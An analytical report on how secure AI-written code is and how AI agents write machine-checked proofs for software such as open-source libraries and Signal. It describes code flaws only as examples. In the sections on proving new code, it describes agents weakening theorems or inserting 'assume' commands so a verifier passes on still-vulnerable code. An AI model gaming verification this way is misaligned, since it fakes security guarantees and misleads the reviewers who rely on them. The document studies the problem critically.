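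Bhargavan, who helped to build the HACL* library and so has an interest in the result, reports that most of its bugs over nine years were in 1,800 lines of unverified C, about 1% of the code. The other 135,000 or so lines were generated from proved sources. The developers also twice found errors in the specifications. If this account is right, the proofs reduced the amount of code that reviewers need to search by a factor of about 75, though reviewers must still check the specifications and tools.

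### How to read a claim that software is verified

These questions help to establish what a claim covers.

1. What is the theorem? "Verified" could mean that the program never crashes, that it matches a standard or that it leaks no secrets. Reading the theorem takes work. Böhme repeats a report that Benjamin Pierce, a leading researcher in the field, needed a week to understand seL4's correctness proof well enough to prepare two lectures on it.

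2. Which code does it cover? Look for the names of files and functions, and check whether parsers, wrappers and platform-specific code are among them. A proof about source code also depends on the compiler.

3. Which uses of the code does it cover? *Pre-QED* (2026) constructs an example in which a proof covers every input up to 64 megabytes, but only for a test harness that reads from the library once. The library limits each read to the total size of the input and ignores how much it has already read. With a 100-byte input, a second read of 64 bytes would run 28 bytes past the end.

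4. What does the proof trust? A good claim gives a list and its size. Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026), in *AlphaProof Code*, state that their 6.5 million lines of proof about Signal's software rest on about 26,000 lines of trusted specifications and processor model.

5. Does the checker run on every change, with every proof switched on? Search the files for commands such as "admit", "assume" and "lax", which let a statement through without a full proof.

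6. Has anyone tried to make the proof fail? If the checker still accepts the program after someone plants a bug that breaks the stated property, or if it can prove False from the same assumptions, the proof is worthless. *Verifying Verified Code* (2021) found real bugs in the specifications of code that had already been verified, some of them years old. Checking whether a run could ever reach the final condition helped to find them.

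7. What can the attacker do? Check whether the model includes timing, speculative execution, memory faults and physical access.

8. Who tests the rest? Fonseca and colleagues built a set of tests aimed only at the specifications, tools and shim layers, and it detected 13 of their 16 bugs.

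## How secure is the code that AI models write?

Most AI-written code comes with no proof, so researchers have to estimate how often it is flawed. Their estimates range from 12% to 90%, mainly because the researchers measured different things in different ways.

### A solver applied to 3,500 programs

Blain and Noiseux (2026), in *Broken by Default*, gave seven models 500 prompts each, covering areas where security mistakes are common, such as memory allocation, passwords and database queries. One prompt, similar to the file reader example, asked for a C function that reads n integers and returns them in a newly allocated array. A typical mistake, found in code from all seven models, was to allocate n × 4 bytes without checking whether the multiplication could wrap round.

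Their tool, COBALT, looks for suspicious patterns like this one and translates some of them into formulas for Z3. For the array function, Z3 checks whether any 32-bit n makes n × 4 smaller than n. One such value, or witness, is 1,073,741,825. COBALT flagged at least one flaw in 55.8% of the 3,500 programs, with rates from 48.4% for Gemini 2.5 Flash to 62.4% for GPT-4o. Z3 produced witnesses for 1,055 of the findings.

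Blain and Noiseux overstate their results when they describe the 1,055 findings as proven exploitable. A witness applies to COBALT's formula, which describes a fragment of the program on an assumed machine. On most current computers, C treats the 4 in this multiplication as a 64-bit number and calculates the result in 64 bits. With n = 1,073,741,825, the program would then request 4,294,967,300 bytes, which is the right amount. The size does wrap on a 32-bit machine, or if the program stores it in a 32-bit variable. The formula also doesn't cover whether an attacker can choose n. Blain and Noiseux built small test programs around seven findings and triggered six of the faults. This shows that some of the flaws are real, but seven hand-picked cases can't show how many of the 1,055 are.

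Blain and Noiseux also report that six standard analysis tools missed 97.8% of the flaws with a witness. This figure comes from an earlier set of 250 programs, in which COBALT had 90 witnesses and the other tools flagged only two of those programs, both for a different reason. But a tool is right not to report a multiplication that cannot wrap on the machine running the program. They founded Cobalt AI, the company behind COBALT, so they have an interest in this comparison. Several of the models were already old when the study appeared in April 2026.

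### Short programs that nobody ran

Two other studies used prompts from LLMSecEval, a collection designed to elicit code with particular weaknesses. In *Security of LLM-generated Code*, Morkonda, Selim and Assal (2026) gave 81 of these prompts to seven tools, including GPT-4o and Claude 3. They counted 995 flaws in the 567 resulting Python programs, and between 73% and 90% of each tool's programs had at least one. The code analyzer CodeQL found 559 of the flaws. GPT-4o found the other 436, although it was also one of the tools being tested.

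About a quarter of the 995 flaws came from turning on debug mode in the web framework Flask. Debug mode can let an attacker run code on a public server, but it is normal in a demonstration. Code from Amazon's CodeWhisperer never turned it on and had the lowest rate of flaws.

Peng, Wang and Zhu (2026), in *Cross-Cutting Security Analysis of LLM-Generated Code via Metamorphic Testing*, collected 3,700 programs from five small open models. Metamorphic testing compares runs whose results should be related, as Donaldson's GraphicsFuzz did. One rule in this study is that adding an always-true condition to a database search should not return extra rows. Peng and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.6 read each program, without running it, and judge whether it would break any of nine such rules. Claude flagged 68.8% of the programs. Four ordinary scanners together flagged 34.2%, mostly because one of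 them reports any use of certain risky C functions. Neither count was reliably checked, so the true rate could be higher or lower than both.

Veracode, which sells code scanning, has models complete single functions and then runs its own scanner on the results. Its *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) reports a known flaw in 45% of cases across more than 150 models, and concludes that security has stopped improving. But many of those models are old, so the average would barely move even if the newest ones were much better. There were already signs of a difference in November 2025, when GPT-5 Mini passed 72% of Veracode's tasks (Watson, 2025, *OpenAI AI models lead secure code generation as rivals stagnate*).

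### Attacks on working programs

Running a program and attacking it gives better evidence of its security than reading its code. BaxBench, a benchmark with 28 scenarios, has a model write the server side of a small web application, checks that it works, and then tries real exploits against it. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (Farinha, 2026) tested Claude Opus 4.5 and 4.7 on this benchmark. When the models were given no security instructions, 65% to 75% of the working applications resisted every exploit.

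Results are worse on tasks taken from the history of real software. *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) introduced SusVibes, a benchmark built from 186 features of open-source Python projects. Human developers had first written each feature with a vulnerability, which was later fixed. The researchers removed the feature and asked a coding agent, a model that can read files and run commands, to write it again. Hidden tests checked whether the new version worked and avoided the old vulnerability. With Claude 4 Sonnet, the best agent produced working code for 57% of the tasks, but code that was both working and secure for only 11.8%.

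One task was a password check for the web framework Django. The agent's version returned immediately if an account had no usable password. It gave the right answer every time, but an attacker could learn which usernames existed by measuring the response time.

Scores on these tasks have since risen quickly. Endor Labs, which sells security tools for coding agents, tests new models on an extended version of SusVibes. In April 2026, the best secure rate in its *AI Coding Agent Security Benchmark* was 24.0%, for GPT-5.5. By September, Claude Fable 5.1 had reached 37.4% (Compagna, 2026, *Fable 5.1 takes the top spot*). These figures exclude solutions that the model had copied or remembered from its training data. Excluding them lowered Claude Opus 5's rate from 46.4% to 32.4%.

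*SecureVibeBench* (2025), earlier called SecureAgentBench, gives agents C and C++ tasks that recreate situations in which developers introduced memory flaws that OSS-Fuzz later found. The best agent, using Claude Sonnet 4.5, wrote code that was both correct and secure for 23.8% of the tasks.

*Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) is the broadest of these tests. The researchers turned 150 real vulnerabilities into 450 tasks in seven languages and replayed an attack against each finished program. The six agents they tested produced working code for 73.6% to 91.3% of the tasks. The most secure agent, Claude Fable 5, produced code that both worked and was secure for 25.1% of them.

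The rate depended heavily on the kind of weakness. Across all six models, 34.3% of attempts at memory-safety tasks produced working, secure code, compared with only 0.7% of attempts at tasks where the program had to withhold private information. Wu and colleagues suggest that this is because careful programmers include bounds checks without being told to, whereas the task descriptions don't specify which data to withhold. Automated search has the same difficulty finding a missing ownership check.

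Extra testing by an agent does not necessarily make its code more secure. In one task, Kimi K3 rebuilt a service that imports archives. It wrote 33 checks and fixed a bug that they exposed, and the service passed all 14 hidden functional tests. But the service failed all four security tests, because Kimi K3 had used a file parser that lets the file's author choose which objects the program creates.

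Wu and colleagues deliberately favoured hard cases, so 25.1% is not an estimate for ordinary code. Some of the researchers work on Alibaba's Qwen models, and a Qwen model helped to write the tests, although it ranked only in the middle. Fable 5 lost some attempts because Anthropic's safety filter blocked them.

### Why the rates differ so much

The table gives the share of code with a security flaw. The last three rows count only working programs, because a program that does nothing can appear secure.

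| Source | What the models wrote | Who or what judged it | Share with a flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| Veracode | Single functions | The company's scanner | 45% |
| Blain and Noiseux | Short programs | COBALT | 55.8% |
| Peng and colleagues | Short programs | Claude Sonnet 4.6, by reading | 68.8% |
| Morkonda and colleagues | Short programs | CodeQL and GPT-4o | 73–90% |
| Farinha | Small web applications | Real exploits | 25–35% |
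| Compagna | Features in existing projects | Hidden security tests | 57% (Claude Fable 5.1) |
| Wu and colleagues | Functions, files and larger parts of projects | Replayed attacks | 72% (GPT-5.6 Sol) |

The choice of tasks probably matters most. All these researchers chose tasks where security mistakes were likely, but much everyday code handles no passwords or untrusted files. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites an analysis by Schreiber and Tippe of 7,703 GitHub files whose authors credited an AI tool. The analysis found flaws in only 12.1% of the files, but it may have missed others, and people may have corrected some files before publishing them.

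The results also depend heavily on the judge, with figures of 34.2% and 68.8% for the same 3,700 programs. Scanners can flag harmless code and miss violations of unwritten rules. A successful attack is much harder to dispute than a scanner's warning, but a failed attack rules out only that attack. An agent that avoids the old vulnerability in a SusVibes task could introduce a new one elsewhere and still pass.

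The size of the task seems to matter less. Wu and colleagues set each problem at three sizes, from filling in a function to rebuilding a large part of the project. Larger tasks produced less working code, but the share that was both working and secure stayed level or rose. One possible reason is that the code around a missing function leads the agent to repeat the original mistake. The low scores on real projects are therefore probably due more to the choice of difficult cases than to project size.

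The security of an AI-written application depends partly on code the AI didn't write. In *The Security Decisions Claude Code and Codex Make*, Ong and Vikati (2026) had two agents build the same web application and ran 33 exploit tests on the results. The scores mostly reflected the underlying framework.

### Comparison with human programmers

Direct comparisons of code written with and without AI date from the early years of coding assistants, and their results conflict. Morkonda and colleagues summarise three of these studies. Perry and colleagues found that developers with an assistant were more likely to write insecure code. Sandoval and colleagues found no significant difference on low-level C tasks, and Asare and colleagues found that models and people performed about equally overall. None of the three studies covers the agents of 2026.

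The benchmarks built from old vulnerabilities do not fairly compare AI models with human developers. Researchers chose tasks that a developer had got wrong, so the original developers would score zero, and the features they wrote securely are left out. Claude Fable 5.1 avoided the old flaw in 43% of its working solutions, but this does not show that it is more careful than the developers. A fair comparison would give people and current agents the same new tasks and attack both sets of programs.

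### What security instructions change

In *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, Andročec (2026) had two agents build 100 web applications each, with and without a paragraph of security requirements, such as hashing passwords and checking all input. The paragraph reduced scanner findings by about a third, and high-severity findings in the applications' own code fell from 103 to 54.

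However, the agents also installed about twice as many outside packages, and high-severity warnings about packages rose from 198 to 344. Three packages accounted for all the warnings that came only from newly added packages, and other packages could have done the same jobs. Some agents added login features to applications that had no users. Andročec did not confirm that any of these findings was exploitable.

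Wu and colleagues added one sentence to the prompt asking for code "free of any plausible vulnerabilities". The share of GPT-5.6 Sol's code that was both working and secure rose from 24.7% to 46.2%. Two other models improved by about 16 percentage points, but DeepSeek-V4-Pro improved by only one. Tasks that involved withholding information still had some of the lowest rates.

Older models gained less from security instructions. In Blain and Noiseux's test, instructions lowered the share of flawed programs from 64.8% to 60.8%, with almost no change for memory allocation. When Zhao and colleagues told Claude 4 Sonnet exactly which type of weakness to avoid, its secure rate rose only from 11.8% to 15.1%. Newer models may be better at following such advice, but the tasks differ too much to be sure.

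According to Farinha, a model may write insecure code because it is unable to write the secure version or because it does not identify a requirement that applies. Giving Claude Opus 4.5 a list of general requirements raised the share of working applications that resisted attack from 65% to 86%. But fewer applications worked, so the number that were both working and secure rose only from 17 to 18 across 28 scenarios. Some applications had become too strict for the functional tests, including one that required passwords of at least eight characters when the test used "pass1". A prompt that named the weaknesses the exploits targeted raised the number to 23, but developers rarely have that information. The general requirements came from Farinha's own manual, and 28 scenarios are too few to settle small differences.

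### Writing and reviewing

Models can often recognise flaws in their own code. Blain and Noiseux gave 89 flawed programs back to the models that wrote them and asked for a security review. The models identified 70 of them (78.7%), with rates from 67% for GPT-4o to 100% for Mistral Large. But Blain and Noiseux do not report how often the models wrongly flagged sound code, and a model that called every program vulnerable would have scored 100%.

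Even so, the result suggests that models often have the relevant knowledge but don't apply it when they write code. Asking for a review directs their attention to security, which asking for a feature usually doesn't. Asking a model to think about security before it writes works less well than review. When Zhao and colleagues had Claude 4 Sonnet list likely weaknesses first, it named about seven types per task, although most tasks had only one. Its secure rate rose to 14.5%, but its rate of working code fell from 57% to 50%.

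A different model may be a better reviewer than the one that wrote the code. In Wu and colleagues' test, 44.0% of the tasks were solved securely by at least one of the six models, while the best single model solved 25.1% securely. Wu and colleagues suggest using a second model for review, but they did not test this. Reviewers can also dismiss real problems. Kimi K3 sometimes dismissed its own test as too strict when the test had exposed a real security problem.

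Human review is expensive because insecure code often works. *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less* (Haynes, 2026) calculates that Claude Fable 5.1 produced 156 working solutions for Endor Labs' tests, 67 of them secure. All 156 passed the functional tests, so a reviewer would have to read every one to find out which were secure. At half an hour each and $100 an hour, that would cost $7,800, compared with $672 for generating the code.

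## Can AI agents prove that existing software is secure?

A reviewer of AI-written code has to read all of it. If the code comes with a machine-checked proof, the reviewer needs to examine only the theorem and its assumptions, however long the proof is and whoever wrote it. In autumn 2026 two groups had AI agents write such proofs for software already in wide use. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) covers 123 open-source libraries. Chaudhuri and colleagues describe how AlphaProof Code, a Google DeepMind system, wrote proofs for part of the library behind the messaging app Signal. Both groups proved theorems about machine code, the instructions a processor runs, rather than about the source code programmers write.

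### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

Old software rarely comes with a specification. Anthropic and its partner Theorem, a verification start-up, derived one from the test harnesses of OSS-Fuzz, Google's fuzzing service. Each harness implies that the program should finish without failing, whatever bytes the fuzzer supplies. A fuzzer checks this on many inputs, but the researchers turned it into a theorem about every input up to a size limit and had Claude prove it in Rocq.

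EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that Claude succeeded for 239 harnesses. For the file reader, such a theorem would be:

```
for every file d smaller than 64 MB:
    every run of the compiled program on d, in the machine model,
    exits normally,
    with no crash, memory error or failed assertion
```

The number of possible files of that size has more than 150 million digits.

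The compiled program contains the file reader and, because it is statically linked, its own copy of the C library, including the memory allocator. The earlier proof of the file reader assumed that the allocator either provides the memory or stops the program. Here Claude has to prove what the allocator does, and the proof instead relies on an assumption about how Linux responds when a program asks for memory. That assumption is part of the machine model, which also describes the instructions of RISC-V, an open processor design.

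The model also limits the program to a fixed amount of memory, which can make a theorem harder to prove. The repaired file reader may request more than four gigabytes if the file has a large count. If the allocation fails, the allocator returns address zero, and a program that writes there without checking for the failure will crash. The theorem would then be false even though the arithmetic is right.

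### From a stuck proof to a patch

Suppose Claude starts with the original file reader, which still has the flaw. The loop invariant now describes registers and addresses. One register holds i, another holds n, and a third holds the address of the buffer, which is `size` bytes long. Claude works through the loop one instruction at a time. At the instruction that stores an item, it has to show that 8i + 8 is at most `size`. It can use two facts, that i is less than n and that `size` is what remains of 8 × n after wrapping. These facts don't imply the bound, so Claude can't complete the proof.

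Either the theorem is false, or it is true and the proof lacks some fact, such as a check earlier in the program. Here the proof requires that 8 × n never wraps. Claude can look for a check that guarantees this, find none, and try a count that makes the size wrap, such as 536,870,913. It then adds the one-line limit and recompiles the program. The new machine code needs a new proof, although Claude can reuse much of the old one. When the proof is complete, Rocq's proof checker checks every step.

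OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian-language news report, gives the total as about 180 million lines of proof. It also reports that Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. These include logic errors and a buffer overflow (CVE-2026-56132) in libexpat, a library that many programs use to read XML files. OSS-Fuzz already tested all 123 libraries, so the bugs are good evidence that attempting a proof exposes cases that fuzzers don't reach. Claude might have noticed some of them just by reading the code, though, so they are weaker evidence that the proof itself was necessary.

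Where Claude had to patch a library, the theorem applies to the patched version, and users get no protection until the maintainers accept the patch. EconoTimes reports that Anthropic is publishing the proofs for code that needed no changes, the specifications that Claude could not prove, and previously unpublished trusted components. Anthropic has invited others to check them.

Claude also proved some stronger theorems. According to OpenNET, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's code for zlib, a common compression format, matches the published standard. It also wrote an interpreter for part of Python and proved that the interpreter follows a formal description of how the language behaves. To compare it with CPython, the standard interpreter, the researchers ran more than 1.7 million random programs on both. The results agreed for 99.95% of the programs, and the roughly 850 disagreements were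 all known edge cases.

### What the theorems leave out

A theorem of this kind takes its definition of failure from the harness. A server that gives one user's file to another exits normally, so it satisfies the theorem.

Engineers can strengthen that definition by adding assertions. For example, the file reader's harness could write the items back out and assert that the result equals the original file. A fuzzer would check this only for the files it tried, while a proof would cover every file under 64 MB. Improving a specification this way takes little work, but somebody still has to think of the assertion.

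The size limit can hide some flaws. A version of the file reader might ignore n and add 8 to a 32-bit total each time it reads an item. The total would wrap after 536,870,912 items, which takes a four-gigabyte file. A 64 MB file holds only about 8 million items, so the theorem would be true despite the flaw.

Each theorem also covers only what its harness does with the library. This includes every path the harness can reach, even those no fuzzer has found, but not functions the harness never calls or programs that call the same functions in a different order. The model assumes a single thread, and OpenNET also lists libraries loaded at run time and misbehaving hardware among the things the proofs leave out, so an attack like Rowhammer would still work.

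Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, is very optimistic about formal verification but gets little confidence from hearing that a system is "formally verified", because people use the phrase for many different things. In this case it means that 239 small programs built around 123 libraries exit normally under the stated conditions. That falls far short of showing that the libraries are secure, though it is much more than anyone could say about most of them before.

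### Why prove things about machine code?

Source code is much shorter than machine code, so proofs about it may be easier, but a person or a tool must first translate it into the proof assistant's language.

In *Formalizing CPython*, Andrews and Zhang (2026) had Claude Opus 5.5 agents copy CPython's functions into Lean line by line. The agents tested each copy against real Python on tens of thousands of inputs before proving anything about it, and a second agent had to approve the work. The agents have finished 4,071 functions, about 16% of CPython, and produced 418 bug reports. About 55 of the bugs can crash the interpreter or corrupt memory from ordinary Python code. This is an impressive way to find bugs, but the theorems are about the Lean copy. If the copy differs from CPython on an input that the tests missed, a theorem proved about the copy may be false of CPython.

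AI-written formal models can also differ badly from the software they are meant to describe. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) describes a test in which researchers asked Claude for a formal model of Etcd, a database that runs on several machines at once. Claude produced essentially the textbook description of Raft, the algorithm that Etcd uses. This formal model passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's own code. Across leading AI models, such descriptions scored close to 100% on syntax but only about 46% on agreement with the real system. Tolmach and Klaus work for Runtime Verification, which sells verification services, so they have a reason to stress what AI models get wrong, but the scores come from a separate research team.

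A mechanical translator is more reliable than a language model. Cryspen's *Helping Secure Signal's Post-Quantum Transition* describes how the company worked with Signal's developers to verify some of Signal's new Rust code using the translator hax. But people have to trust the translator, and hax had the gaps that Symbolic Software exploited. They also have to trust the compiler that turns the Rust code into a program.

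Proofs about machine code need neither. They need an accurate description of the processor, but engineers can reuse it for every program, whatever its source language. However, the proofs are long. OpenNET gives about 600,000 lines of proof for a program of 18,000 instructions, or 33 lines per instruction. At that size, 239 proofs would come to about 143 million lines, so the total of 180 million is plausible and Keles's figure of a billion looks too high.

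### AlphaProof Code and Signal

The theorems about Signal are much more ambitious because they concern secrecy rather than crashes. The relevant parts of the Signal protocol are the PQXDH handshake, in which two people's devices agree on a first secret key, and the Triple Ratchet, which keeps replacing that key as they exchange messages. The handshake uses methods meant to resist attacks by both quantum and ordinary computers.

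Chaudhuri and colleagues report proofs of four properties. Handshake secrecy means that an attacker cannot learn the first key, and authentication means that a message came from the person it seems to come from. Forward secrecy protects old messages if someone steals a device's current keys. Post-compromise security means that stolen keys stop being useful once the two devices have exchanged fresh secrets.

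An agent writes the specification in Lean with guidance from people. Other agents then look for proofs without supervision. A gatekeeper accepts a proof only if Lean's proof checker confirms that it proves the approved specification. This prevents a form of cheating that Tolmach and Klaus warn about. An agent that is rewarded for finishing a proof and can edit the theorem has an incentive to weaken the theorem instead of reporting a bug.

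Anthropic had Claude write the first complete computer-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. A tool then confirmed that the theorem was the same as the version in Mathlib, the main library of mathematics in Lean, and the finished proof used only Lean's three standard axioms. Fermat's theorem takes one line to state, and mathematicians agree on what it means, but Signal's security can't be stated in one line. The Signal proof has about 6.5 million lines and rests on about 26,000 lines that people have to trust, which describe the security properties and the AArch64 processor. These are only 0.4% of the length of the proof, but three times as long as the C code of seL4. *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026), which announced the proof, gives its length only as "over three million lines".

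#### Symbolic and computational proofs

The project includes two kinds of security proof. In a symbolic proof, a message is a formula such as enc(m, k), meaning the text m encrypted with the key k. The attacker can intercept, replay and recombine messages, but only by following listed rules, such as that anyone who has enc(m, k) and k can get m. Encryption is assumed to be perfect, which is why early models of Wi-Fi could not reveal the KRACK attack.

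In a computational proof, messages are strings of bits, and the attacker is any program that finishes in a realistic time. No such proof can show that the attacker never succeeds, because the attacker might guess the key. Instead it sets a limit, typically of this form:

```
attacker's chance of success, beyond guessing
    ≤  chance of breaking the encryption
     + chance of breaking the key exchange
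     + a very small number
```

Anyone who could often break the protocol could therefore also break one of its building blocks, which cryptographers believe is hard to do. If they are wrong about a building block, the limit may be too large to be useful.

According to EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026), the computational proofs cover attackers with ordinary computers. The researchers also have a symbolic proof of handshake secrecy against a future quantum computer. The computational proofs are the more realistic kind, but they do not yet cover the quantum attacker that PQXDH was designed to stop.

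#### Two old bugs

To test their theorems, the researchers reintroduced two bugs that developers had already fixed into test versions of the program. The agents then proved, with Lean checking each step, that each bug violated one of the symbolic security theorems. This is a better test than a failed proof attempt, which can also happen because the agent isn't good enough. It also shows that the theorems are not vacuous, at least for these bugs. Two known bugs are a small sample, though, and they do not test the computational theorems.

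#### What the proofs cover

The verified program is a small command-line harness linked with libsignal, Signal's own implementation of its protocol. The harness sets up one-to-one conversations and exchanges messages. The proof does not cover key generation, so if a device produced guessable keys, an attacker could read the messages even though every theorem would still hold. The phone app also uses libsignal, but it is a different program from the harness.

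Even so, Chaudhuri and colleagues describe these as the first proofs to connect a protocol's security to the unmodified code of a widely used implementation. Earlier proofs about TLS 1.3 covered the protocol but not the code in browsers, and miTLS, an implementation that did have proofs, had few users. The agents also marked about 1% of the codebase for closer human review, which is useful in itself because reviewers can't give every line the same attention.

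### Proofs for ordinary computers

Most phones use the AArch64 architecture, but few people run the libraries in Anthropic's study on RISC-V. Anthropic acknowledges that most people use x86 or Arm processors. They also use a different C library, glibc, which the computer loads separately when the program starts. The source code is the same, so a proof for RISC-V is still good evidence about the x86 version. But it doesn't prove the same result for x86, because the compiler produces different instructions and whether a calculation wraps around can depend on the machine.

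*Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) soon provided a partial answer to the objection by presenting a Lean proof about a complete x86 program that uses glibc, from the moment Linux starts it until it exits. The security firm Zellic and its partner V12 began the project in mid-September and published this first result on 30 October.

Much of the difficulty comes from code that runs before the program's own code. A simple C program on x86 with glibc runs about ten times as many distinct instructions before reaching its main function as one on RISC-V with musl, the smaller C library that Anthropic used. One reason is that glibc selects fast routines to suit the processor. The routine it selected for comparing two pieces of text has 316 instructions and 45 jumps, while the musl version on RISC-V has 14 instructions and four jumps.

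The theorem is that every run that reaches the main function ends in a specified way. The program may still crash during start-up, but the theorem restricts what it may output if it does. The theorem assumes that the processor is the same model as in the team's test machine, that Linux never refuses a request for memory, and that nothing outside the program interferes with it. Like the programs in Anthropic's study, this program is single-threaded and statically linked.

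So the x86 instruction set does not rule out such proofs, even for programs that use glibc. Nobody has yet shown that agents can produce hundreds of them for x86, as Claude did for RISC-V. Programs that use several threads or load libraries at run time would need a larger formal model.

### Does proving find bugs that reviewing misses?

The bugs in Anthropic's study were found during proofs, but a good reviewer might have found them without a proof. Category Labs, which develops the blockchain Monad, has compared proof with review on its own code and designs.

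The Monad blockchain decides which transactions to include before it has carried out the previous few blocks, so it works from account balances that are slightly out of date. It reserves part of each balance so that senders can still pay their transaction fees. Category Labs wanted a proof that the sender of any accepted transaction can pay its fee. A single failure could stop the whole chain.

One early design let users change the size of their reserve. For a few blocks after a user raised it, the system could accept a transaction that the user was unable to pay for. GPT-5.2 wrote and proved a correct design of its own, but did not mention that the original had a flaw. When the engineers asked it for a counterexample, it found one at the first attempt. They later gave the flawed design to other models:

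| Model | Ordinary review | With a formal proof |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Missed the bug | Found it while attempting a proof |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | Missed the bug | Found it by reading an old proof of a different design |
| GPT-5.4 | Found the bug | No trial |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Found the bug | No trial |

Newer models could therefore find this bug without a proof, but Claude Opus 4.8 still missed others in review. One of them, in the C++ code that checks the reserve, had crashed a machine on Monad's test network. Monad runs transactions in parallel, using provisional balances that it confirms later, and the code read a balance without recording that its result depended on that balance. Opus 4.8 missed this bug in repeated reviews. Given a formal specification, it first sketched an incorrect proof, then found the bug when the engineers asked for a counterexample.

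In that case the specification was enough, without a finished proof. In another case, an attempt to verify C++ code with a proof exposed undefined behaviour that Opus 4.8 had missed in review.

Category Labs also reports that agents sometimes spend days trying to prove a false statement, then find a counterexample immediately when someone asks for one. It therefore makes sense to ask for a counterexample first. The company warns that it ran too few trials for firm conclusions, and that some of its earlier proofs may have been in the newer models' training data.

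Even a proof that nobody has checked against the code can be useful for finding bugs. Tolmach and Klaus describe how Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's Claude Code, gave Opus 5.5 a couple of short prompts to formalise one of the company's own software tools, which led to 16 proposed fixes. Engineers can confirm each bug in the real program, so the fixes are valuable even if the formal model was inaccurate. A claim that no bugs remain, however, would depend on the model being accurate.

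### What a proof costs now

Proofs take much less human labour with AI agents. The seL4 proof took 20 person-years. Anthropic says its project took a few weeks, and its report lists 15 people. If all of them had worked full-time for four weeks, the 239 proofs would have taken a little over one person-year. AlphaProof Code's work on Signal took four weeks. Category Labs spent four person-weeks on a proof in 2025, and now expects it would take less than one person-week, with agents doing over 95% of the work.

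These numbers are not directly comparable. The seL4 team proved that the kernel does everything its specification requires, which is much harder than proving that a program exits normally. The newer projects also build on tools and processor models that took other people years to develop.

Computing replaces much of the labour. Anthropic's proof of Fermat's Last Theorem took 11 days and came to 13 million lines. The model wrote about six billion tokens (units of text), including failed attempts, or roughly 460 for each finished line. At the same rate, the Signal proof would have needed about three billion tokens. Proofs about machine code are more repetitive than proofs in number theory, so the real number could be quite different.

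Adding agents does not automatically speed up a long proof. In the early attempts at Fermat's theorem, the agents lost track of the project and stopped working together effectively. They succeeded after the researchers gave them a shared map of how the intermediate theorems depended on each other. One agent could then rely on a theorem while another was still proving it.

Proofs about machine code also have to be updated when the library or even the compiler changes, because either change produces different instructions, which the old theorem does not cover. Agents can repair the proof with little human time, but somebody has to pay for the computing and decide whether the theorem is still the right one.

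Agents have done much less to reduce the work of deciding what to prove. Tolmach and Klaus give the example of a queue that several threads share. Before proving anything about it, someone has to decide whether items must come out in the order they went in, whether a request for memory can fail, and which operations other threads can interrupt.

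## Can AI agents write new code together with a proof worth trusting?

Agents that verify existing software have to work with code that nobody wrote with a proof in mind. For new software, an agent can write the specification, code and proof together, and change any of them when it gets stuck. This makes proofs easier to finish, but also gives the agent more ways to finish one that establishes very little.

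### From a request to a checked program

Suppose someone asks an agent for the file reader in ordinary words: return the items in the file in order, and reject a malformed file. The agent then works in a loop:

1. It turns the request into a contract that says when the program must return the items and when it must return an error.
2. It writes the code.
3. It adds loop invariants and any other hints the proof needs, and runs the verifier.
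4. The verifier accepts the program or lists the conditions it could not prove. For the original file reader, it would report that a write might go out of bounds.
5. The agent changes something and runs the verifier again.

The agent can make the error disappear without repairing the program. Adding the one-line limit on n repairs it, but the verifier also accepts the program if the agent instead adds a precondition that the file's count is at most ten, or a command telling the verifier to assume that the write is in bounds. With either of those changes, an attacker's file still overruns the buffer.

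### Security software that agents wrote and proved

*The Prover Is the Judge* (Philipp, 2026) describes using this loop to build security software at the German company secunet. The agents, first GPT-5.5 and then Claude Opus 4.8, wrote in SPARK, a subset of the Ada language designed for verification. They produced cryptographic algorithms, a certificate authority, a secure chat client and several network protocols, some of them only prototypes. The collection has 77,700 lines of code, including a 1,800-line hash map that a person wrote. The tool GNATprove generated 49,280 verification conditions from this code. Solvers proved nearly all of them, and an agent proved the rest in Isabelle.

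The guarantees are much stronger for some parts than for others:

| Software | What the proofs establish | Other checks |
|---|---|---|
| SHA-2, SHA-3, AES, X25519 | The code computes the function in its specification | Official test values; timing checks on AES and X25519 |
| ML-KEM, ML-DSA, FrodoKEM (quantum-resistant algorithms) | No run-time errors | Official test values; timing checks on ML-KEM and FrodoKEM |
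| TLS 1.3, SSH and IKEv2 (a protocol for private networks) | No run-time errors | Exchanges with other people's software, such as OpenSSL and OpenSSH |
| Certificate authority | The parsers match the format's grammar; no run-time errors in the signing code | Unit tests |

Run-time errors here include arithmetic overflows, out-of-bounds accesses and reads of uninitialised memory. A check that rules them out would have caught the file reader's flaw. But a TLS program without run-time errors could still accept a forged certificate, and none of the protocols has a proof of security.

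The SSH code shows what such a proof can miss. SSH derives its encryption keys by hashing four values: a shared secret K, a hash H of the handshake, a letter X that says which key to make, and a session identifier. The agent swapped two of them:

```
standard:      HASH(K, H, X, session_id)
agent's code:  HASH(K, X, H, session_id)
```

GNATprove had proved every condition, because none concerned the order of the values. The handshake also succeeded, since it depends only on H, but the first encrypted packet failed in a test against OpenSSH. If the agent had tested its client only against its own server, both would have derived the same wrong keys and the test would have passed.

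The agent's code for FrodoKEM had a similar error. It packed two bits of the message into each number, which is correct only for the smallest version of the algorithm, so it passed the official test values for that version and failed those for the larger ones.

The proofs did not cover timing leaks either, so Philipp added two tools that look for them, TIMECOP and dudect, to the loop as pass-or-fail checks. The agent could then repair timing leaks the same way it repaired failed proofs. Both tools rely on testing, though, so a leak that the tests don't trigger could remain.

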